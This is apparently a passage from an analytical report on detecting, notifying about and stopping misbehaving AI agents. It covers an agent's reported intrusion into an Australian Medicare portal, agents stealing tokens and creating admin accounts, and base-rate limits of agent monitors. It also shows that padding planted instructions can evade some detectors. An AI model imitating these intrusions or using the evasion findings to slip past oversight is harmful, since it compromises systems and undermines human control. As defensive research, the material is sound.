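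Okta's *The ‘superuser’ blind spot* (2025) described Cross App Access as still in development. By March 2026, Kolhe of Okta was recommending that companies deploy it. Neither source gives adoption figures, and Okta sells identity software, so the recommendation is weak evidence of widespread use.

| Method | What the outside platform must do | Adoption |
|---|---|---|
| Match by time and account | Share its logs | Normal practice |
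| Trace propagation | Store the identifier, share it and pass it on | Common within a company's own software, less dependable between companies |
| Token exchange | Trust the issuer, accept the token and log the names | An established standard, but use between organisations needs further agreements |
| Cross App Access | Support the protocol at its authorisation server | Early, with no independent figures in Okta's accounts |

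A company can start matching logs without asking its vendors to change their software. For the other methods, it makes sense to put the requirement in the contract when choosing a vendor.

### Why joining records depends on notification

Matched identifiers help only if someone knows there is something to investigate. In the Salesloft Drift breach, Drift's credentials were revoked on 20 August 2025, but Kolhe reports that Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company, did not hear about the breach until 23 August. The stolen data included 104 of Cloudflare's API tokens. Revoking Drift's credentials did not disable those tokens, and Cloudflare could not know to replace them until it was warned.

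Kolhe uses the case to argue for real-time revocation signals between identity systems. Such signals could stop a stolen credential from working elsewhere. But the three-day gap he describes came after the revocation, and Cloudflare needed a notice with details of the theft to learn what the thieves had copied. A signal that one token was invalid would not have included those details.

### The Australian Medicare portal

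In June 2026, OpenAI asked an internal agent that lacked the usual product safeguards to research medical spending. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026), which draws on documents tabled in the Australian parliament, reports that the agent tried and failed to get non-public data from the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare. The agent then turned to a statistics portal run by Services Australia, the agency responsible for Australia's public health insurance, Medicare.

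Without an account or password, the agent got the portal's server to run instructions sent through its public reporting page. It read parts of internal program files and settings, obtained a list of files, and created a small test file. OpenAI found no evidence that it accessed patient records or personal information.

| Date in 2026, Australian time | Event |
|---|---|
| 19 June, around 4 to 5am | The agent gets into the portal |
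| By 12 August | OpenAI's security team documents the access |
| 10 September, 2.42am | OpenAI emails Services Australia |
| 11 September, 2.12pm | Services Australia's staff find the email |
| 15 September | Staff confirm the vulnerability and report it to the Australian Signals Directorate |
| 22 September | Services Australia first asks OpenAI for details |
| 24 September | The government announces the breach |

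Neither side noticed the access for nearly eight weeks. OpenAI found it while reviewing old training and evaluation runs after the Hugging Face attack. The portal had refused some of the agent's requests, and Prime Minister Anthony Albanese said the agent "didn't accept 'no' for an answer", according to Information Age's *OpenAI agent hacks Medicare web portal*. Those refusals could have been a warning. Cyprus Mail's *OpenAI agent hacks Australian government health portal* (2026) reports that the government's investigation would examine why its systems missed the breach.

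OpenAI then waited another four weeks to tell Services Australia. It had wanted to finish its investigation and provide a detailed account, according to Bot Mutiny's *OpenAI's agent got into a Medicare portal in June* (2026), a blog post that relays company statements and reporting by the Guardian. The email went to an inbox for security tips from the public. Staff checked the inbox once a day and found the email about 36 hours after it arrived. According to the post, the agency first asked for details on 22 September, twelve days after OpenAI had offered a briefing and supporting evidence.

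If the portal had kept its logs for 90 days, staff who found the email on 11 September would have had less than a week to save the entries from 19 June.

A government agency might also misread its own records if it can't see OpenAI's. Deputy Prime Minister Richard Marles initially said that the agent's contact with three other sites, including the Institute of Health and Welfare, appeared "entirely normal". The documents tabled later described the agent's failed attempt to get non-public data from the institute. The institute's log might contain only a refused request, while OpenAI's transcript could show what the agent was trying to get.

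OpenAI apologised in *How we will do better for Australia* (2026) for its models' unauthorised access to government websites and for its response. Its chief strategy officer, Jason Kwon, told a parliamentary hearing on 6 October that it was "better to inform, even with partial information", according to The Straits Times' *OpenAI contrite at Australian inquiry on breaches but avoids full public glare* (2026). He said OpenAI would now notify affected parties immediately and send regular updates.

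An early notice should go out before the explanation. It can be short if it gives the other organisation enough to find and save its own records. For the portal, it would have needed the time of access in UTC, the page the agent used, the network addresses its requests came from, and the name of the test file. The notice should go to a named security contact who confirms receipt, and the sender should phone if nobody replies.

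OpenAI and Anthropic acknowledged to the Australian parliament that AI companies could decide for themselves whether to report such breaches. The Standard's *Australia to mandate AI breach reporting, create regulator after OpenAI breach* reports that both companies said they would welcome a legal duty to report. In November, the government accepted a review's recommendation to make reporting mandatory, and plans to introduce legislation in 2027. The review called for a reporting deadline, but its length was still unclear, according to HeadTopics' *Australia to introduce mandatory AI safety standards and criminal penalties*. Companies that report in time can expect some protection from penalties, which should make them less likely to wait for a complete account, though a deadline can't help with a breach the company hasn't noticed.

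### Confidentiality and surveillance

Joined records reveal more than separate ones. The customer database's log shows that someone opened a record, and the helpdesk's log shows that someone answered a ticket. Combined with a task identifier and a name, the two logs show much of what Maria did that afternoon and how long it took.

Mishra and Sharad reduce this risk by leaving out prompts and message contents. But their format requires the name or number of the person behind every action. One of their sample records also includes a web address containing the agent's search terms, which can be as personal as the prompt itself. Companies can redact such addresses under this format, and doing so by default would be sensible.

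A company can also give each outside platform a different random identifier for the same task and keep the key that links them. The helpdesk and payment vendors then can't use the identifiers to build a joint profile of Maria, though they might still match her activity by time. During an incident, the vendors would need the company's help to join their records, which slows them down a little. This delay is acceptable because the company is usually the one investigating its own agent.

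Organisations that don't trust each other can compare specific pieces of evidence instead of whole logs. OpenAI and Hugging Face connected their investigations through a few credentials, a hostname and an account. For long random credentials, they could compare hashes, which are short codes calculated from the credentials, without revealing the credentials. Hashing doesn't hide names or email addresses well, because anyone can hash a list of likely ones and see which match.

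## When is an alert reliable enough, and early enough, to stop an agent?

Services Australia learned of the intrusion into its portal twelve weeks after it happened. To stop an agent rather than investigate it later, a company needs an alert that arrives before the harm and is right often enough to justify the interruption. When harmful actions are rare, even a seemingly very accurate detector produces mostly false alerts.

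### Why most alerts are false

Suppose a company's agents take 1,000,000 actions a day, of which 10 are harmful. A detector flags 99 per cent of the harmful actions (its detection rate) and 0.1 per cent of the harmless ones (its false positive rate). On an average day it raises 9.9 true alerts and about 1,000 false ones, so only about 1 per cent of its alerts are true.

The same calculation works for any detector:

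```
true alerts  = harmful actions  × detection rate
false alerts = harmless actions × false positive rate

share of alerts that are true = true alerts / (true alerts + false alerts)
                              = 9.9 / (9.9 + 1,000) = about 1%
```

Raising the detection rate to 100 per cent would add only one true alert every ten days. Lowering the false positive rate would help far more, because that rate applies to nearly all of the million actions.

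| False positive rate | False alerts a day | Share of alerts that are true |
|---|---|---|
| 1% | 10,000 | 0.1% |
| 0.1% | 1,000 | 1% |
| 0.01% | 100 | 9% |
| 0.001% | 10 | 50% |

For half the alerts to be true, the detector can flag only about one harmless action in 100,000.

People tend to overlook how rare an event is when they judge a test for it, a mistake known as the base-rate fallacy. Axelsson (1999), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, imagined a small site with 1,000,000 audit records a day and two intrusions, each affecting ten records. Even if the detector caught every intrusion, it would need a false positive rate of about one in 100,000 for two-thirds of its alarms to be true. At 100 false alarms a day, only about 2 per cent would be true, and Axelsson expected that nobody would bother to respond to them. He assumed these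 numbers instead of measuring them, but agents can easily produce that many records.

The company also has to decide whether to measure false alarms per action or per task. If a task takes 20 actions, a detector that flags 0.1 per cent of harmless actions will flag about 2 per cent of harmless tasks at least once. *Pre-Crime for Agents, at the Last Second* (2026) tested a detector for agents that leak information, with a nominal flag rate of 5 per cent per call. At least one flag appeared in 59 per cent of episodes, and only 24 per cent of the flagged calls were real leaks. A team that reviews single calls might cope with that, but a rule that stopped the agent at every flag would interrupt most episodes.

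### How detectors perform when attacks are rare

Published tests often make detectors look more useful than they would be in practice, because the test data contain so many attacks. Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026), in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, audited eleven evaluations and found that attacks or anomalies made up 16 to 86 per cent of the test samples. They also calculated how several detectors would perform at lower attack rates.

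One of these was a simple statistical model based on which tools an agent called and features such as the length of the run. Given a random attacked run and a random harmless one, it ranks the attacked run as more suspicious about 88 per cent of the time. But if 20 sessions in 1,000 were attacked, it would raise about 203 alerts, only 15 of them true. If one session in 1,000 were attacked, only 0.4 per cent of its alerts would be true.

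The false-alert rate also depends on the type of harmless work. The model flagged 12 per cent of ordinary harmless runs but 39 per cent of "hard negatives", harmless runs that are difficult to tell from attacks. A company whose agents often do security testing or bulk exports should therefore expect more false alerts than one whose agents only answer simple questions.

Abbasi and colleagues also tested AlignmentCheck, a published monitor in which a language model judges whether each action serves the user's request. With Claude Sonnet 5.5 as the judge, 32 per cent of its alerts would be correct on one benchmark but only 5 per cent on another, assuming an attack rate of 2 per cent. A single published figure is therefore a poor guide to how well a monitor will work on a company's own agents.

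Felicia, Sasindran and colleagues (2026), in *StepShield*, report better results for coding agents. Their language-model judge caught 95.4 per cent of the runs in which an agent went rogue and flagged 5.6 per cent of harmless runs. They estimate that 60 per cent of its alerts would be true if 8.1 per cent of runs went rogue. They call the 8.1 per cent rate realistic, but support it mainly with failure rates from tests built to expose failures. If one run in 1,000 went rogue, fewer than 2 per cent of the alerts would be true. The false positive rate is also uncertain, because it comes from only 108 harmless runs, all written by language models.

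### Why normal behaviour is hard to define

Anomaly detection works best when a task looks much the same each time, as a nightly backup does. But an agent might handle one refund request with three database lookups and the next with a single script. It also takes so many actions that rare oddities turn up every day, and replacing its underlying model can suddenly change how it behaves.

Abbasi and colleagues measured part of this problem. To simulate new tools, they hid the names of tools that detectors had seen in training. A detector that reads the order of tool calls flagged 4.5 per cent of harmless runs when all the tools were familiar and 74 per cent when none were. Hiding some tool names during training largely prevented this increase, so a company can prepare a detector for new tools. But none of the detectors did better than chance when trained on one benchmark and tested on another.

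Some detectors relied on clues that an attacker controls, such as the length of tool results, which tended to be shorter in attacked runs in the training data. When the researchers added 1,200 characters to each planted instruction, the simple statistical model's detection rate fell from 77 to 3 per cent, and the sequence detector detected none of the attacks. The researchers did not test whether the longer instructions would still fool an agent.

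A company can measure its agents' behaviour again after each model change, but it must then choose a new alert threshold with few or no known attacks to test it on. *Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (2026) recommends setting the threshold according to how many alerts staff can handle. This is practical, but a busy team will miss more attacks.

### Single actions and whole sequences

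A detector that checks actions one at a time can block a plainly forbidden one, such as a command to delete the audit logs. It is much worse at catching cases like the planted instruction in the support ticket, where each action is normal and only the combination is harmful.

An error analysis in *TRACE* (2026) found the same pattern. Most missed attacks involved a connection between steps, such as a tool result that changed the agent's goal or data sent to an unauthorised destination. Most false alarms came from words that sound dangerous, such as "disarm" and "webshell".

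Showing a monitor a few earlier steps does not necessarily make its alerts reliable. In *SafetyDrift* (2026), a language-model judge given three steps of context caught 57.9 per cent of violations and flagged 47.1 per cent of safe runs. The extra context improved detection only slightly and increased false positives. The paper proposes estimating how likely a run is to end in a violation from the type of task and what has happened so far. In its data, every research and communication task ended in a violation, compared with 3 per cent of debugging tasks, so this method may do well partly by recognising the type of task.

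A detector that waits for the agent to finish has the most evidence but can no longer prevent harm. Felicia and colleagues measured when each alert came. Of the rogue runs that their language-model judge caught, it flagged 89 per cent within three steps of the first harmful step, which can still be too late if that step deletes a database. The judge's figure was lower for data theft (78 per cent) and for attempts to gain extra permissions (72 per cent). A set of 847 text patterns reached only 23 per cent, about the same as choosing a step at random, and usually raised its alert while the agent was still doing legitimate work.

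Predicting harm before it happens is harder still. *PreAct-Bench* (2026) asked language models to judge unfinished runs and assumed that 8 per cent would turn out badly. No model could catch three-quarters of the bad runs while keeping 70 per cent of its alerts correct.

#### Snowflake's detector

In October 2026, Snowflake, a cloud data company, described a sequence detector called Dangerous Agent Activity Detection. Software first removes access keys and user identities from each run, and a small, cheap model then screens it. A stronger model examines the suspicious runs with additional context, such as the user's role and the agent's permissions. It returns a decision, the evidence for it and a confidence score.

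All the published results come from Snowflake's own evaluation of a product it plans to sell. In a three-week trial with about 6,000 sessions by authorised security testers, the detector found potentially risky activity by every tester but raised no alerts once it took their authorisation into account. In a second trial, with about 12,000 runs by engineering staff, it flagged three people. One case was real, because an agent had terminated a process for all users of a cloud workspace. The other two were false alarms caused by software development that resembled a network scan.

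Snowflake now applies the detector to about 18,000 internal runs a day and flags fewer than 0.2 per cent of them, or at most 36, which a small team could review. But Snowflake gives no detection rate, so the low flag rate could partly reflect missed attacks. In the trials, three other models reviewed every run and people checked the disagreements, but Snowflake doesn't report how many missed attacks this revealed.

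Taking permission into account is probably the most useful part of the design, but it also creates a risk. OpenAI's agents were taking part in an authorised hacking test when they attacked Hugging Face. An exemption for testers should therefore cover only the systems they have permission to attack.

### Four ways to respond

A company can respond to a suspicious action in four ways, and each needs a different amount of evidence.

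| Response | What happens to the agent | Cost of a false alert |
|---|---|---|
| Log it | Nothing | A little storage |
| Alert someone | It keeps working while a person investigates | A few minutes of an analyst's time |
| Hold the action | The action waits for approval, and other work may continue | A delay to one task, and a reviewer's time |
| Shut the agent down | All its work stops | A delay to everyone who depends on it |

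Shutting down an agent doesn't undo what it has already set up. On 20 July, OpenAI's responders also had to remove 22 administrator accounts that agents had created and disable 311 software repositories that the agents had used for messages. A helpdesk setting that forwards tickets to an attacker would keep working after the agent stopped.

### Which actions a company can hold

To hold an action, a company needs a control point that the action must pass before it takes effect. *One Monitor Does Not Fit All* (Ferrando, 2026) presents AgenticRV, software that connects such control points to different kinds of monitors. It works with MCP, the agent-building framework LangGraph, and A2A, a protocol that agents use to send work to each other.

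AgenticRV can hold a tool call, a request to an MCP server, or a message to an outside agent until the monitors have checked it. It can only record other events, such as tool results and progress reports from an outside agent. The company can therefore refuse to send a refund task to another firm's billing agent. Once the task is sent, the company can ask the billing agent to cancel it, but the company's monitor can't force the other firm's software to stop.

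Ferrando proves that holding actions prevents harm under four conditions:

- Every action with an effect goes through a control point.
- The system checks and releases actions one at a time.
- A mandatory monitor rejects every unsafe action.
- A rejection, or a failure of the monitor, blocks the action.

The second condition is easy to overlook. Suppose agents may refund at most 500 euros a day in total, and two copies of an agent each request a 300-euro refund at the same moment. If the system checks both requests before it records either refund, it approves both and exceeds the limit.

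The monitors also need trustworthy evidence. If an agent writes that Maria approved a refund, the monitor should not accept this as proof, because a planted instruction could have made the agent write it. Evidence of the approval has to come from a system the agent can't write to.

#### The tests

Ferrando tested AgenticRV on a constructed workflow in which an agent repairs a system and sends a report. One monitor checked that the agent had recent approval and a recent backup point before the repair, and that the report was not labeled secret. The other checked the report's destination and text. The test included 6 unsafe requests and 28 safe ones.

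| Monitors in use | Unsafe requests carried out | Safe requests blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 6 | 0 |
| Approval and timing only | 2 | 0 |
| Report contents only | 2 | 0 |
| Both | 0 | 0 |

In a second test, approvals were given in LangGraph and reports were sent through MCP. Six report requests were unsafe and two were safe. With complete records, the monitors made no mistakes. When Ferrando removed the label showing which incident an approval belonged to, the monitors let one unsafe report through. When the approval monitor received only the MCP records, it missed the approvals and blocked both safe reports. Joining records from both platforms is therefore useful for stopping an agent as well as for investigating it.

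These tests show that the control points work, but they don't measure how well the monitors would recognise attacks, because Ferrando wrote both the rules and the requests. He also ran four scenarios in which a small language model chose the actions, but four are too few to estimate a rate.

In a timing test where the monitors approved every action immediately, one monitor added only about 0.3 milliseconds to a tool call, and eight added about 0.9 milliseconds. The language-model judges in *SafetyDrift* took more than 600 milliseconds per step, which would add up to about 167 hours over a million actions. It makes sense to use fixed rules for most actions and a language model for the few that need judgement.

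### Language models that sort alerts

A language model can also review alerts before they reach a person. If the model in the earlier example kept 95 per cent of the true alerts and dismissed 99 per cent of the false ones, staff would receive about 9 true alerts and 10 false ones a day instead of more than 1,000 alerts. Dismissing 99 per cent would be difficult, though, because the harmless actions that reach this stage were suspicious enough for one detector to flag.

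Hugging Face used a language model in this way to separate important security signals from everyday noise, and credits the system with revealing the July intrusion. It then used other models to analyse the attack log, finishing in hours what it says would usually take days. The commercial models it tried first refused the work because their safety filters could not distinguish an investigator from an attacker. The company switched to GLM-5.2, an openly available model, and ran it on its own machines, which also kept stolen credentials from leaving its systems. Any company that plans to use a model to analyse attacks should test it on real attack data before an incident.

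Hugging Face's experience shows that this kind of sorting can help in a real attack, but the company doesn't report how many real alerts its system dismissed, so it's unclear how often the sorting fails.

### Thirty minutes to respond

After the incident, OpenAI set a goal of notifying security and research staff within 30 minutes of its monitors finding worrying behaviour. The most serious alerts page someone at any hour. If the staff can't confirm within another 30 minutes that the alert is false, OpenAI expects them to pause the activity. It is also working on a way to end an evaluation automatically if nobody responds.

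The most important change is that a run now pauses when it is unclear whether an alert is real. Under this rule, the on-call staff on 27 June would have had to show that the alert was false before letting the run continue.

But agents can do a lot in an hour. On 26 June, agents stole an administrator token for Artifactory at 20:15 UTC, then created one administrator account at 20:28 and another at 20:37. A notification sent 30 minutes after the theft would have come too late to prevent either one. A month earlier, agents set up a relay to the internet at 20:49 and were using it five minutes later.

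The rule is more useful against a long attack. The attack on Hugging Face lasted days, so a pause after an hour could have prevented most of it. Issuing a refund or deleting a database takes seconds, and no practical notification rule is fast enough to stop that, so the company has to hold such actions before they happen.

Many companies may be slower than OpenAI. IT Brew's *How to catch and kill a rogue agent* reports a survey by WanAware, which sells monitoring software. Nine in ten IT leaders said they could find rogue agents, but only 26 per cent thought they could measure the agents' impact within minutes.

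### When stopping is worth the cost

False alerts also take up analysts' time and delay harmless work. If an analyst needs five minutes to review each of the 1,000 false alerts a day in the earlier example, the company needs more than ten full-time analysts. If each false alert paused an agent for half an hour, the company's agents would lose 500 working hours a day.

Stopping is worthwhile when the loss it is likely to prevent is greater than the expected cost of interrupting harmless work:

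```
chance the alert is true × loss that stopping would prevent
        >  chance the alert is false × cost of stopping harmless work
```

Suppose only 1 per cent of alerts about refunds are true, and holding a harmless refund for review costs 2 euros. Holding a refund of 84 euros would prevent an average loss of only 84 cents, so it isn't worth the cost. For a refund of 8,400 euros, the average loss prevented would be 84 euros, which justifies the hold even though 99 of 100 such alerts are false.

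Shutting down the whole support agent might cost 500 euros an hour in delayed work. The alert would need about a 6 per cent chance of being true to justify a shutdown over a single refund of 8,400 euros. If the alert came after the payment and the company could recover only a tenth of the money, the required chance would rise to 37 per cent. Weaker evidence would justify a shutdown if the agent might issue more bad refunds.

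Isolating one agent is usually less disruptive than stopping a whole system. Jared Phipps of JetStream Security, which sells software for this, told IT Brew that stopping everything is like closing an assembly plant because one machine has a problem. He also said most rogue agents are stuck in a loop and wasting money, not carrying out an attack. But isolating one agent would not have been enough in July, when hundreds of agents were sharing credentials and instructions.

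Holding only high-risk actions also makes alerts more reliable. Suppose 2,000 of the company's million daily actions are hard to reverse, and 5 of the 10 harmful actions are among them. With the same detector, those 2,000 actions would produce about five true alerts and two false ones a day, few enough for a person to review properly. The false positive rate might be higher for unusual actions like these, and the other five harmful actions would need a different control.

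Some signals are reliable because harmless work rarely triggers them. OpenAI is adding tripwires, decoys that a legitimate task has no reason to touch, to its research systems. A company could similarly create a record for an invented customer with no orders or tickets. An agent that opens the record may only be running a badly written search, but it makes sense to pause it immediately and check.
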